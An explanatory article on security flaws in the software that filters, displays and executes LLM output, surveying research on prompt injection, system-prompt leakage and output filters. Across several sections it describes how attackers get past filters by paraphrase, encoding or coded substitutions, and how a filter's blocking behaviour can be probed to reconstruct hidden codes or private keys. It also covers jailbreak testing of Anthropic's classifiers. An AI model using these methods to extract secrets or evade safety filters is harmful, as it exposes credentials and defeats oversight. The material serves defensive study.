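# Attacks on how deployed language model systems filter, display and act on model output

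## What happens to a model's answer after it is generated

A large language model is a program that takes in text and predicts how it continues. People who use a chatbot or an office assistant reach the model through a wrapper, the ordinary software that assembles the model's input, collects its output and determines what happens to it. *LLM in the Middle* (Moia, Sanz and colleagues, 2025), a survey of threats to such products, defines an LLM system as a set of software components which, besides the model, may include a user interface, databases and modules for processing input and output.

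The software that handles a model's answer has its own security problems. Depending on the product, it may block the answer, display it as a formatted page with links and images, run it as a program, or treat it as a command to send an email. Programmers wrote the code for each step expecting the text to look a certain way, and an attacker who can influence the text can try to violate that expectation.

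In early accounts, the software around the model did little with its output. *Identifying and Mitigating Vulnerabilities in LLM-Integrated Applications* (Jiang, Xu and colleagues, 2023) described an application that adds its own data to a user's question, sends it to the model, does some post-processing on the raw response and returns the result. Newer systems run in a loop. In the reference design of *SoK* (2026), a systematisation of attacks on tool-using agents, the model selects an action, the software carries it out, and the result goes back to the model until the goal is met or the budget runs out. An output in that design may be the final answer or another action.

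### One request, stage by stage

Suppose an office assistant can open documents and send email. A user asks it to summarise a document that someone at another firm has shared, and to email the summary to a colleague, Dana Ortiz.

The wrapper first gives the model the developer's instructions, the user's request and a description of the available tools. When the model outputs a request for the document, the wrapper fetches the document and adds its text to the model's input. The model receives all of this as tokens, which are short pieces of text, often a word or part of one, represented as numbers. It also generates its output one token at a time, and the wrapper converts the tokens back into characters. The resulting text contains both a summary for the user and a request to send an email, which later software has to tell apart by their format.

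If the product has an output filter, the filter receives the answer, sometimes with the conversation that led to it, and passes on the same text, an altered version or a refusal. If the product displays the answer while the model is still writing it, the filter must either hold text back or evaluate unfinished sentences. Some filters check only part of the output. For example, a filter that inspects the summary shown to the user may not inspect an email the model also wrote.

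The summary then goes to the renderer, which converts it to HTML, the language of web pages, and passes it to the browser. Some characters in the summary carry formatting. In Markdown, a notation common in chat products, asterisks make a word bold and brackets make a link. The browser acts on the HTML it receives. For example, it fetches images from whatever address the text gives, which is one way that just displaying an answer can leak data.

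The email takes a different route. It leaves the model as a tool call, a structured request to run a named function with given arguments. Tool calls usually use JSON, a text format that writes data as pairs of names and values. The developer has declared the tool in advance, with a name, a description and a schema, which states what arguments the tool accepts and of what type. A declaration and a matching call might look like this:

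```
{"name": "send_email",
 "description": "Send an email from the user's account",
 "parameters": {
   "type": "object",
   "properties": {"recipient": {"type": "string"},
                  "body": {"type": "string"}},
   "required": ["recipient", "body"]}}

{"name": "send_email",
 "arguments": "{\"recipient\": \"Dana Ortiz\", \"body\": \"Summary: ...\"}"}
```

The backslashes in the last line show that the arguments are a JSON document stored inside a string, so any program that reads them must parse them again. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz (2026), in *Oops!... I Parsed It Again*, traced how often this happens. The model provider's interface turns the generated text into a tool-call object. Gateways that translate between providers' formats may parse the call and rewrite it. The developer's framework parses it once more, looks up the tool and often validates the arguments against the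 schema. Validated arguments can still contain unexpected fields, because an object schema accepts fields it does not define unless its author forbids them.

The guard then receives the call, decides whether to allow it, and usually writes a log entry. The guard can be a program that applies a policy, a data-loss filter that looks for confidential material, or a person who clicks "approve". In this example, it might check that Dana Ortiz works for the user's company. The executor then carries out the call. It decodes the arguments into its own data structure and often inserts them into a command, a file path or a database query. It then returns the result, which the model reads as new text.

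The software that executes a tool call is often written by a third party. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard for connecting models to tool servers, and its messages follow the same pattern. The wrapper, acting as the client, sends a `tools/list` request to a server, which returns definitions that each include a tool's name, a description and a JSON Schema for its input (Model Context Protocol, 2025). Once the model has picked a tool, the client sends `tools/call` and gives the result to the model. Because users can attach several servers at once, the Model Context Protocol project (2026) pointed out in March 2026 that the risk depends on the whole session and cannot be judged from any single server. A server that opens shared documents and a server that sends mail may both be harmless alone, but attaching them to the same assistant creates a path from a stranger's document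 to an outgoing message.

*Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) likens the whole sequence to compilation, which turns a human-readable program into machine instructions step by step. The comparison fits the later steps better than the first, in which the model translates the user's request into a tool call. A compiler follows fixed rules, whereas the model predicts the tool call, and any text in its input may influence that prediction.

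### Who attacks, and from where

Some attackers are the product's own users, who want an answer that the provider blocks. They write the request and receive the result, so they can see what failed and try again. The attack succeeds once readable text gets past the output filter and reaches the screen.

An outsider has no access to the conversation, but can redirect what the model does by placing instructions in a web page, email or document that it will read. This is called indirect prompt injection. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by Britain's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, David C gives the example of a recruitment system that scores CVs, where an applicant hides a line of text telling the model to approve the application. With the office assistant, anyone able to edit the shared document can do the same, and the user is now the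 victim. But as Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz stress, planted text reaches a tool call only if the model copies it there, and the model may rewrite it, shorten it or refuse.

An attacker who controls a tool server or the connection has less need for persuasion. A hostile server supplies the schema and description that both the model and the guard rely on. A hostile gateway or proxy can change a call after the model writes it. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz treat the server and the connection as separate positions and report results for each, because an attack that works from one may fail from the other. An attack can also combine positions, as when a malicious server writes a note that the assistant later reads.

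Jiang and colleagues examined a more extreme version of this third attacker, a hostile application. They built a shopping chatbot on GPT-3.5 and GPT-4, both since superseded, and wrote 50 queries asking it to compare products. In one attack, the application used the model's answer to build a new prompt and had the model produce a slanted replacement. Human reviewers found the intended bias in 83% of answers with GPT-3.5 and 80% with GPT-4, against 2% and 0% when nobody interfered. A dishonest application could just as well edit the text directly, because the user sees only what the application delivers and cannot compare it with what the model wrote. Jiang and colleagues proposed digital signatures so that user and model can each verify where a message came from and that nobody altered it on the way.

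### Why model output counts as untrusted input

Developers tend to trust data that their own system has produced, and a model's answer looks like such data because it comes from a service they pay for, under instructions they wrote. But its content depends on all the text the model has processed. OWASP, the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, is a nonprofit that publishes widely used lists of software risks. Its *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* warns that because a prompt can control what the model generates, passing the output to other components resembles giving users indirect access to them. It advises developers to treat the model "as any other user" and validate what it sends to the rest of the system.

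Web developers learned this lesson from two older flaws, SQL injection and cross-site scripting. In the first, an application pastes a visitor's text into a database query and the database runs part of it as a command. In the second, a site pastes a visitor's text into a page and another visitor's browser runs it as a script. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (2026) finds the same structural failure when a chatbot's answer goes unchecked into a web page. Here, though, the model composes the harmful text, whereas the attacker of an ordinary website supplies it directly. A scan of the incoming request may therefore find nothing, because the script does not exist until the model writes it.

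David C warns against taking the comparison between prompt injection and SQL injection too far. Parameterised queries prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the values to the database separately, so the database never treats a value as a command. A language model has no such separation, because it receives instructions and data as a single sequence of tokens and predicts the next one. David C argues that prompt injection may therefore never be fully preventable, and that designers should assume an attacker can do anything the model's tools allow.

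Even when a document has misled the model, the software that handles the model's output can still prevent some attacks. Browsers can distinguish markup from plain text, and databases can distinguish commands from values. If the assistant's summary is only meant to be read, the application can encode it so that the browser displays any script as harmless text. These defenses don't help when the model chooses an action. An email to the wrong person can be perfectly well-formed, and encoding won't correct the recipient, so the system also needs a check on whether the email should be sent.

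### OWASP's name for the flaw

OWASP defines improper output handling as "insufficient validation, sanitization, and handling of the outputs generated by large language models" before other components receive them. Its examples of places where output can take effect include system shells, browsers, databases, file paths and email templates. The damage ranges from a script running in a user's browser to an attacker running code on the server. In one OWASP scenario, which involves no attacker, a chatbot passes its response unchecked to an extension that also has administrative functions, and the extension shuts down for maintenance. OWASP covers false output under a separate heading.

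OWASP's first list, from 2023, placed the entry second, as *LLM02*, Insecure Output Handling. The 2025 edition renamed it Improper Output Handling and numbered it LLM05:2025. The edition published on 3 August 2026 keeps the newer name but places the entry last, as LLM10:2026 (OWASP, 2026). Anyone reading an old audit report could misread a number given without its year, because the earlier numbers now refer to other risks. A comparison of the editions by Respan (2026), a vendor of testing tools, shows that LLM02 now means disclosure of sensitive information and LLM05 means data and model poisoning.

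Output handling's fall in the ranking does not necessarily mean that these flaws have become rare. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), an account by another security vendor, explains that three quarters of the ranking came from a community vote and one quarter from 7,714 recorded incidents. Prompt injection ranks first, but would have dropped out of the top ten on incident count alone. Invicti attributes output handling's lower rank to other risks on the list being more urgent, and notes that the entry has expanded to cover terminals and programming tools that execute control codes hidden in text, and renderers that automatically fetch outside resources. Respan says the entry now also covers insecure code from coding assistants. Excessive agency, meaning more permissions or autonomy than a system needs, rose from sixth to third, and OWASP has had a separate list for autonomous agents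 since December 2025. The assistant's misdirected email could reasonably be classified under any of these headings.

### Whether the check and the sink read the same text

OWASP's remedy of validating the output before use works only if the component that checks the text interprets it the same way as the component that acts on it. The same condition applies at every stage of the office assistant's request. An output filter compares characters or scores a passage, and then a person reads it for its meaning. A sanitiser determines which parts of a page are safe, and then the browser interprets the page again. A guard parses a tool call, and the executor parses it again, perhaps with a different library. If the results differ, the guard can approve one call while the executor runs another.

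A parser differential occurs when two programs read the same bytes as different data. Neither program needs to have a bug, so testing them separately tends to miss the problem. One could arise from the sample request that the Model Context Protocol (2026) project published with its July 2026 revision. The request names the tool in both a header and the JSON body, so a gateway can route it without opening the body. If the gateway also uses the header to decide whether to allow the request, that check is effective only if the server ensures that the two names match.

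People who approve a model's tool calls may not see exactly what will be executed. A user who clicks "approve" on an email to Dana Ortiz has read a dialog box that some component generated from its own parse of the call's arguments, while the mail server will act on the arguments themselves.

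## Filters that compare the answer with forbidden text

The simplest output filter has a list of text that must not reach the user, and searches each answer for that text. Companies use such filters to keep passwords, hidden instructions and copyrighted passages out of a model's answers. Ordinary code does the search, so the result doesn't depend on what a user has persuaded the model to do. But the search finds only the forms of the text that its programmer anticipated. A user can also often tell when the filter has blocked something, and use that to work out what is on the list.

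### Exact, pattern and overlap matching

Suppose a support assistant has the access code MAPLE-4821 in its system prompt, the hidden instructions that a developer places before every conversation. An exact-match filter blocks any answer that contains this ten-character string. If the product displays text while the model is still writing, the filter has to hold back the latest nine characters, because they could be the start of a match.

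A pattern filter searches the answer for text of a given form, such as five capital letters, a hyphen and four digits. Programmers usually describe the form with a regular expression, a compact notation for text patterns. The filter catches codes that the company creates after writing it, but it also blocks harmless part numbers of the same form.

Neither method suits a long text such as a news article. A filter that looks for the whole article would pass a copy with the last sentence missing. Developers therefore split the protected text into n-grams, which are runs of *n* consecutive words or tokens, and look for any of them. *Language Models May Verbatim Complete Text They Were Not Explicitly Trained On* (2025) formally defines such a filter for removing documents from training data, and the definition works equally well for answers. Let *F* be the set of forbidden n-grams. The test *f*ₙ(*x*,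 *F*) equals 1 if any n-gram of the text *x* is in *F*, and 0 otherwise. The filter keeps only texts that score 0. A smaller *n* makes the filter stricter, because two texts that share a run of ten words also share runs of five. If *n* is too small, the filter blocks common phrases.

### Checking against the training data while the model writes

Language models can reproduce passages from their training data word for word, which may expose personal information or infringe copyright. *Preventing Verbatim Memorization in Language Models Gives a False Sense of Privacy* (Ippolito, Tramèr and colleagues, 2022) introduces a filter to prevent this, called memorization-free decoding. It checks for overlap with the training data at every token rather than after the answer is finished.

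At each step the model assigns a probability to every possible next token. The decoder, the code that picks one, joins its candidate to the *n* − 1 tokens before it and looks up the resulting n-gram in a set built from the training data. If it finds the n-gram, it sets the candidate's probability to zero and picks another token. With *n* = 4 and a training text that contains "the quick brown fox", a model that has written "the quick brown" cannot continue with "fox". One lookup per candidate is enough, because earlier steps have already checked the earlier n-grams. The system could instead check the finished answer and generate a new one if it matches, but a model that gives a memorised passage a very high probability may produce it every time.

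The lookup must be fast and the training data may take up terabytes, so Ippolito and colleagues used a Bloom filter, which is a long row of bits that all start at zero. To add an n-gram, a program computes several positions from it and sets the bits there to one. To look up an n-gram, the program computes its positions again and checks those bits. If any bit is still zero, the n-gram was never added. If all are one, it was probably added, although other entries may have set those bits by coincidence. A Bloom filter can therefore block an innocent phrase, but it never misses an n-gram that was added to it.

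For the Pile, a public training collection of about 800 gigabytes, the Bloom filter took up 1.6 gigabytes. Ippolito and colleagues saved space by leaving out 10-token sequences that were not repeated in the data; storing all of them would have taken 40.5 gigabytes. They accepted this omission because models mostly memorise repeated text, but a model could still copy a passage that appeared only once.

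Near copies are the larger problem. When Ippolito and colleagues applied the filter to GPT-Neo, a family of openly available models, the models sometimes continued a memorised passage with a misspelling, different punctuation or "&" for "and". A reader would recognise the passage, but no run of ten tokens matched. They found the same weakness in GitHub's coding assistant Copilot. Its optional filter blocked suggestions that shared about 150 characters with public code, but Copilot still reproduced well-known code with the variables renamed, and sometimes changed capital letters or spacing without being prompted. Ippolito and colleagues sent their paper to GitHub and OpenAI before submitting it, and report no fix.

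### An adaptive attacker against nine defenses

In *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models*, Deep, Emmons and colleagues (April 2026) reported the strongest result so far in favour of matching filters. They built an assistant on Gemini 2.5 Pro, with Google's safety filters turned off, and put three secrets in its system prompt: an authentication token, a database ID and an escalation code. A second system, running on the same model, tried to extract the secrets. It sent ten attacks per round, scored the replies, rewrote the five most successful attacks, and mixed in strategies it had seldom tried.

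The score ranged from 0 to 1. Each secret found in a reply added 0.30, the assistant's name added 0.10, and each run of seven or more words from the system prompt added 0.05. Anything above zero counted as a leak, and 0.9 counted as critical. Deep and colleagues tested nine configurations, most for up to 500 rounds.

| Configuration | Result |
|---|---|
| No defense | Full disclosure at round 9 |
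| Screening of the user's message by patterns and a model | Critical at round 39 |
| Security rules in the system prompt | Critical at round 49 |
| User's message wrapped in tags that mark it as data | Critical at round 84 |
| System prompt declared to outrank the user | Critical at round 247 |
| Security rules at both ends of the prompt | Critical at round 277 |
| All defenses except the output filter | 23 of 5,000 attacks leaked, none scoring above 0.10 |
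| Output filter alone | No leaks |
| All defenses, including the output filter | No leaks |

The output filter blocked any reply that contained substrings of the system prompt. Deep and colleagues ran each of the two configurations that used this filter three more times and again found no leaks. Each run had 500 rounds, with 5,000 attacks in total. They report 15,000 attacks across all six runs, but that would match the three runs of only one configuration; six runs make 30,000.

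Several defenses looked sound in short tests. With security rules at both ends of the prompt, the worst score in the first 25 rounds was 0.05, but in the longer campaign, scores stayed near zero for hundreds of rounds and then jumped to 0.95.

The filter's perfect record is less informative than it looks, because the filter and the score check for nearly the same text. A reply scored above zero only if it contained a secret, the assistant's name or a run of words from the system prompt, and the filter blocked replies containing text from the system prompt. Suppose the secret were MAPLE-4821 and the model replied that the code is the tree whose leaf is on Canada's flag, a hyphen, and forty-eight twenty-one. The reader would have the code, but the filter would find no match and the score would be zero. Deep and colleagues concede that substring matching misses paraphrases and that encoded output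 can evade both their filter and their score.

An attack that extracted the secret in another form scored zero, so the scoring did not favor keeping it among the five attacks that the system rewrote for the next round. Even 500 rounds therefore did little to test the filter's known weakness. The tests also used single messages, so they did not cover attempts to collect a secret piece by piece over a conversation.

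Deep and colleagues say the filter succeeded because it only had to look for the few secrets in a prompt, whereas an attacker can phrase a request in endless ways. That explains why the filter outlasted the screening of users' messages, but each secret can also be written in endless ways. Most of the authors work for Swept AI, which sells this kind of testing, and the paper recommends the company's tools by name.

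The experiment does show that a filter outside the model stops literal copies even when the model outputs the secret. This is useful because literal copies are common. *Eight in Ten LLMs Leak System-Prompt Secrets* (Serpa, Rocha and Pedrini, 2026) gave 363 models a random 16-character code to protect, and an attacking agent steered by a researcher extracted it from 296 of them. The paper counted only exact copies as successes, so an exact-match filter would have blocked every successful reply. An attacker who met such a filter would have had a reason to ask for the code in another form.

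### Normalising the text before matching

A filter can catch some variants by normalising both texts, which means converting them to a standard form before comparing them. It might change all letters to lower case, remove spaces and punctuation, and replace look-alike characters from other alphabets. MAPLE-4821, "Maple 4821" and a version with a space after every character would then all become `maple4821`. The filter uses the converted text only for the comparison, so the user still receives the original answer.

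If a filter converts text to a standard form before comparing it, the conversion has to cover the variations the model actually writes. Copilot's documentation said its filter ignored whitespace, but Ippolito and colleagues found copied code that passed the filter with only its whitespace changed. They suspected that the model had replaced tabs with spaces and that the filter did not treat the two as equal.

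Heavier normalisation also blocks more harmless text. With spaces and punctuation removed, the stock list "maple 48, 21 oak" contains the forbidden string `maple4821`. No fixed list of conversions covers every cipher, translation or description. *Membership Inference Attacks Against In-Context Learning* (2024) notes that when a filter blocks output that overlaps with the prompt, a user can get around it by asking for encoded text.

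Comparing meanings instead of characters only partly solves the problem. *PromptKeeper* (Jiang, Jin and He, 2024) tested a filter that converted the answer and the system prompt into lists of numbers representing their meaning, and blocked answers that were too close to the prompt. This filter worked better than instructing the model to keep the prompt secret, but it could miss a translated prompt because the model that produced the numbers was trained mainly on English. A trained classifier can recognise more variants, but it makes errors of its own.

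### How a filter reveals what it blocks

Even a filter that catches every copy can reveal what text it blocks. *Privacy Side Channels in Machine Learning Systems* (Debenedetti, Severi et al., 2023) showed this for filters that block output copied from the training data. If the filter never lets a training passage through, an attacker can infer that any passage that appears in an answer is not in the training data.

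A missing passage is harder to interpret because the filter may have blocked it or the model may never have generated it. Debenedetti and colleagues found two ways to tell these cases apart.

The first works when users can turn the filter off, as they could in Copilot. With the filter off, the attacker looks for a prompt that makes the model produce the passage in question, then enters the same prompt with the filter on. If the output changes, the filter must have caused the change, so the passage is in the training data; otherwise, it is not. The test is inconclusive if no prompt produces the passage with the filter off.

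When a filter is always on, the attacker writes a prompt that makes the model almost certain to generate the passage. Language models tend to continue repeated patterns, so the prompt repeats the passage many times and stops just before the end of the last copy. If the rest of the passage doesn't appear, the most likely explanation is that the filter blocked it.

Debenedetti and colleagues used this to estimate when GitHub had collected Copilot's training data. They sampled changes from over the years to tqdm, a popular Python library for progress bars, and tested whether Copilot could produce the new code from each change with the filter on. Copilot produced some older code that an ideal filter would have blocked, probably because the filter matched text only approximately. But it could produce the code from every sampled change made after October 2021, so they concluded that the training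 data ended around then. The date matches the cutoff of other OpenAI models of the period. The attack did little harm because the code was public, and the paper mentions no change to the filter.

Their second experiment recovered secrets. They took three GPT-Neo models and built a Bloom filter from all the 20-token sequences in the models' training data. To simulate a training set that contained secrets, they then added 1,000 private keys to the filter, each 512 bytes long and of the kind administrators use to log in to servers. The models had never seen the keys, so whatever the attack recovered came from the filter.

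Such a key file begins with a standard header line, which the attacker knows. From there, the attacker tries each possible next token, uses repetition to test whether the filter blocks it, adds the blocked token to the known text and moves on to the next position. Because the filter blocks short sequences, the attacker can confirm the key one token at a time instead of guessing it all at once.

The test was right more than 99.9% of the time, but with over 10,000 possible tokens at each position, an error rate of 0.1% would produce about ten false candidates. Debenedetti and colleagues therefore followed each candidate until it reached a dead end, starting with tokens common in random keys.

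| Model | Keys recovered | Mean number of queries |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-Neo, 125 million parameters | 90.3% | 376,000 |
| GPT-Neo, 1.3 billion parameters | 90.0% | 338,000 |
| GPT-Neo, 2.7 billion parameters | 89.8% | 344,000 |

Model size made almost no difference, as expected if the filter is the source of the leak. The attack needs many queries, so a provider could make it slow and conspicuous by limiting or monitoring repetitive requests. Changing how the model is trained would not help, because the filter would still consult the original data. This is true even of differentially private training, which adds noise so that a model reveals little about any single training example.

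A filter that guards a system prompt has the same flaw. A user who knows that the access code is MAPLE followed by four digits can ask the assistant to repeat guesses and see which one disappears. If the filter blocks only the complete code, this takes at most 10,000 guesses. If it also blocks partial copies, the user can find the digits one at a time, in at most 40 guesses. Matching shorter fragments stops more copying but makes the forbidden text easier to reconstruct. A long random code is safe from guessing only if the filter gives no sign of a partial match.

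### Whether later filters still leak

Freeman, Rippe and colleagues (2024), in *Exploring Memorization and Copyright Violation in Frontier LLMs*, found a similar leak in OpenAI's commercial service while testing how readily models reproduce articles named in the *New York Times* lawsuit against the company. OpenAI's filter stopped the copying effectively, but anyone could find out whether it covered a given text by asking the model to repeat that text. If the filter covered it, the reply arrived slowly or not at all, and a field in the response gave the reason for stopping. The filter covered some of the newspaper's articles but not others, along with parts of a documentary film. Freeman and colleagues treat a block as an implicit admission that the model produces infringing text, but when the user has supplied the text, a block shows only that OpenAI had listed it. The paper describes no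 later change to the filter.

Jiang, Jin and He showed that a hidden prompt can also leak in this way, and proposed a fix. They used the example of an email assistant whose system prompt set a 100-word limit. Their filter blocked any answer whose probability under the model suggested that it depended on the prompt. The assistant returned nothing when asked directly for the limit. But when asked to repeat sentences that stated limits from 20 to 200 words, it repeated most of them and returned nothing for those near 100.

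Their repair hides blocks from the user. When the filter detects a leak, the wrapper discards the answer and generates another from a dummy prompt of similar length that contains only general instructions. In the test, the assistant then repeated every guess, right or wrong, so the reply did not reveal whether a guess was right. The replacement must not take noticeably longer, because Freeman and colleagues could detect blocks from timing alone. For answers that appear as the model writes them, Jiang, Jin and He propose switching to the dummy prompt partway through instead of starting again.

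The repair works because a model without the secret can repeat a user's guess without revealing whether it is correct. If the wrapper also ran an exact-match filter on the replacement, it would block the correct guess and restore the leak. The repair does not work for memorization-free decoding, which is meant never to output a training passage, even one the user has just typed, and an attacker can always test that guarantee. Jiang, Jin and He evaluated their method only on two small open models, and it needs token probabilities that many commercial services do not provide.

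Removing the filter might not stop the guessing, because the model's own refusals may differ when a guess is right. Serpa and colleagues saw behaviour in one model, Xiaomi's MiMo-v2.6-Pro, that could allow such guessing.

### Keeping secrets out of the prompt

Developers can avoid most of these problems by never giving the model the secret, but many still include it. Yang, Zeng and colleagues (2026), in *Understanding and Mitigating Prompt Leaking Attacks in Real-World LLM-Based Applications*, tested 200 applications on each of six commercial platforms, including OpenAI's GPT Store. Between 81% and 93.5% of the applications on each platform revealed their system prompts. About half of those that leaked had instructions not to reveal them.

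Most of the leaked prompts contained only the application's instructions, but 1.6% exposed access secrets. One popular travel planner's prompt contained the key to a mapping service, so anyone who extracted the prompt could use the service at the developer's expense. All six platforms acknowledged the reports, and Alibaba and Baidu rated the problem medium severity. Yang and colleagues still consider it unresolved because the platforms have no standard, effective fix.

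A secret in the prompt can influence answers that never mention it. In *LLMs Leak Secrets Through Unrelated Outputs*, Bhardwaj, Kaya and colleagues (2026) put a four-digit PIN in the system prompt of the openly available model Qwen3-8B and asked for lists of ten random even numbers. They threw out every list that contained the PIN, a rearrangement of its digits or a number that differed from it in one digit. Then they ran the same model with different candidate PINs in the prompt and calculated how probable each candidate made the remaining lists. For each candidate, they averaged the log probability over the tokens in each list and added up the averages.

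With about 20 lists per PIN, the attack identified 24 of 50 PINs exactly, out of 10,000 possibilities for each, and had the correct PIN among its top five guesses for 36. The attack needs the model's weights and a close approximation of the prompt, so it does not directly threaten a service whose model is private. It also worked less well on other models, recovering one of six PINs from Phi-3.5-Mini and none of six from OLMo-2-7B. But a filter that compares the answer with forbidden text could not have stopped it, because the lists contained nothing to match.

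The fix is to keep the credential in the software that uses it. If the support assistant needs the code MAPLE-4821 to open a customer's record, the model can request the record through a tool call, and the server can add the code when it carries out the request. The model never receives the code, so an attacker who misleads the model may still be able to misuse the tool during that conversation, but cannot extract the code and use it elsewhere.

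## Filters that use a classifier to judge the answer

An exact-match filter can block an access code because the developer knows the exact text to search for. Instructions for making a chemical weapon have no fixed wording, so a filter that blocks them has to respond to meaning. An output classifier is a model trained to do this. It gives each answer a score, usually between 0 and 1, that estimates how likely the answer is to be harmful.

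Anthropic introduced a system of this kind, called Constitutional Classifiers, in 2025. Its researchers wrote a "constitution" of rules on which content to block and which to allow, used language models to generate examples of both, and trained the classifiers on them.

### Scoring an answer as it streams

Developers use a streaming classifier for products that display an answer while the model is still writing it. The classifier updates its score as new tokens arrive, so the wrapper can cut the answer off partway.

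*HaloGuard 2.0* (Lenin, Sangameswaran and S, 2026) describes a streaming filter that anyone can download. At each token, the filter estimates the probability that the answer so far is unsafe, given the user's prompt. It stops the answer if one token scores at least 0.975 or if two in a row score at least 0.70. If successive tokens score 0.20, 0.85, 0.40 and 0.30, the answer continues, because 0.85 is below 0.975 and the next score is below 0.70. If the third token scored 0.75 instead, the filter would stop the answer there. The higher threshold is for harmful answers of only one or two words, which a rule requiring a long run of high scores would always miss.

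A streaming filter can act at the wrong time as well as misjudge the content. A dangerous procedure may begin with the same words as a textbook overview or a refusal. If the filter reacts to those words, it interrupts legitimate answers, but if it waits for more evidence, the user may already have read something harmful.

Many products score the user's request too. McKenzie, Hollinsworth and colleagues (2025), in *STACK*, give the combined rule. Let *a*(*q*) be the input classifier's score for the request *q*, and let *b*(*r*) be the output classifier's score for the answer *r*. With thresholds *t*₁ and *t*₂, the wrapper delivers the answer only if

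*a*(*q*) < *t*₁ and *b*(*r*) < *t*₂.

If the request and answer thresholds are both 0.5, a request that scores 0.1 is still refused when its answer scores 0.6. Lowering either threshold catches more harmful exchanges but also blocks more harmless ones. With a streaming output classifier, the answer has to pass at every step, so a long harmless answer has many chances to be blocked by mistake.

### What false alarms cost

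The first Constitutional Classifiers refused 0.38% of queries in ordinary use. *Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026) reports a rate of 0.05% for Anthropic's next system. Most of these refusals are probably mistakes, because few people ask a chatbot about weapons. If ten queries in a million were harmful and both filters caught them all, 3,790 of the older filter's 3,800 refusals would be false alarms, as would 490 of the newer filter's 500.

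The new design explains only part of this improvement. Cunningham and colleagues also tested their own version of the old design, with its thresholds set to refuse 0.1% of the conversations in WildChat, a public collection of chatbot conversations. This version refused 0.073% of queries on Anthropic's live traffic. The 2025 system also increased computing costs by 23.7%, according to Anthropic.

### Answers that make sense only with the question

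The old design used separate classifiers for the request and the answer, and the output classifier received only the answer. Some answers are ambiguous without the request. "The third one, but use twice as much" could be about cake or explosives. A user can exploit this by telling the model to substitute ordinary words for sensitive ones, so that the answer looks harmless to the output classifier but the user knows what it means. Cunningham and colleagues found attacks of this kind against the old design. They also found that the input classifier failed to recognise some harmful requests when they were spread across a longer, harmless text.

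Such disguises make the model less accurate. Cunningham and colleagues tested Claude Opus 4 on GPQA Diamond, a set of very difficult multiple-choice science questions. Its accuracy fell from 74.2% to 32.3% under one attack and to 49% under another. Guessing among the four options would score about 25%. An attacker who needs reliable technical instructions therefore loses much of the model's usefulness. But the gap between the two results suggests that some disguises reduce accuracy much less than others, and Cunningham and colleagues expect attackers to look for them. Neither attack used a code that depended on the question, so that technique's effect on accuracy remains unmeasured.

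An exchange classifier receives the request and the answer together. It scores the request first, then rescores the conversation as each batch of answer tokens arrives. Because it sees the request, it has the key to any code the request contains. It may also recognise a request scattered through other text once the model starts to reassemble it. To avoid repeating work, the system saves its computations on the request and reuses them for each new batch.

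McKenzie and colleagues chose answer-only classifiers for their own experiments because a user might word a request in a way that misleads both the input classifier and an exchange classifier, which reads the same words. An answer-only classifier receives that wording only if the model repeats it. Which risk is greater depends on how well each classifier withstands attack, so Cunningham and colleagues compared them by having people try to break both.

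### How hard the exchange classifier was to break

The testers looked for universal jailbreaks, strategies that defeat a model's safeguards across most questions in a field. They had eight target questions about chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. For each question, language models listed the details a harmful answer would contain and then graded the testers' results against that list. An answer counted as harmful if it earned at least half the score of an answer from an unprotected model. An attack counted as a high-risk vulnerability if it succeeded on more than five of the eight questions.

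Testers found 13 high-risk vulnerabilities in 695,000 queries to the old design and 2 in 226,000 queries to the exchange classifier, about half the rate per query. These counts are small enough that the difference could be due to chance. If both systems had been equally easy to break and every query were an independent attempt, the exchange classifier would have had two or fewer of the 15 vulnerabilities about a quarter of the time. The systems also protected different models, although Cunningham and colleagues doubt that this affected the comparison much.

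Testers also needed more time to find a successful attack on the exchange classifier. They found four attacks on the old design that got the model to answer all eight questions in at least half the detail of an unprotected model, and reported that these took an average of 27 hours to find. Only one attack did this against the exchange classifier, and it took 100 hours.

### Cheaper screening with a cascade and a probe

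The exchange classifier needed 50% more compute than the earlier pair of classifiers because it used a larger model to check the answer. Cunningham and colleagues reduced the compute needed with a cascade, in which a small classifier screens every exchange and passes suspicious ones to a larger classifier. A false alarm from the small classifier uses some extra compute but does not produce a refusal, so its threshold can be low.

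The cascade's small classifier used about a third as much compute as the large one and passed about 10% of traffic on to it. If checking one exchange with the large classifier takes 1 unit of compute, the cascade takes about 0.33 + 0.10 = 0.43 units. The cascade, newer models and more efficient software together reduced the exchange classifier's compute by a factor of 5.4.

Paid testers found five high-risk vulnerabilities in 569,000 queries to the cascade, and none of these attacks produced detailed answers to all eight questions. According to a footnote, experts outside the bounty programme did find universal jailbreaks for this system, with substantial effort and automated tools. The paid testers' results therefore understate what a skilled and well-equipped attacker can do.

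The final version replaced the small classifier with a linear probe. As a language model processes text, each of its layers produces a list of numbers called activations. The probe multiplies these numbers by learned weights, adds the results and converts the total to a probability. Because the model computes the activations anyway, the probe adds almost no computation. For Gemma 3 27B, an open model from Google, Cunningham and colleagues estimate that a probe would need about 377,000 arithmetic operations per token. Running a separate model with four billion parameters would take about eight billion.

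Training the probe was harder, because each label applied to a whole exchange. Two exchanges might begin with the same harmless text, but only one might later turn harmful. Standard training would push the probe towards a score of 0.5 throughout the shared opening. Cunningham and colleagues instead gave the most weight to tokens that the probe already scored as harmful. The probe could then give the opening a low score with little penalty, but a confident false alarm in a harmless exchange still incurred a large one. They also averaged scores over 16 tokens so that one unusual token could not trigger the filter.

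In the final system, the probe passes about 5.5% of traffic to a classifier built from Claude Haiku 4.5. The system combines their raw scores, giving the probe a weight of 0.55 and the classifier 0.45. In tests on recorded attacks, a probe and a classifier together did better than either alone, partly because they made different mistakes. The probe flagged harmless scientific requests more often.

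Over an estimated 1,736 hours and 198,000 attempts, testers found one high-risk vulnerability in the final system but no universal jailbreak that got detailed answers to all eight questions.

| System | Computing cost (old design = 100) | High-risk vulnerabilities | Refusals per million queries |
|---|---|---|---|
| Old design, separate classifiers | 100 | 13 in 695,000 queries | 730 |
| Exchange classifier | 150 | 2 in 226,000 | 380 |
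| Cascade | 27.8 | 5 in 569,000 | 360 |
| Final system with probe | 3.5 | 1 in 198,000 | 500 |

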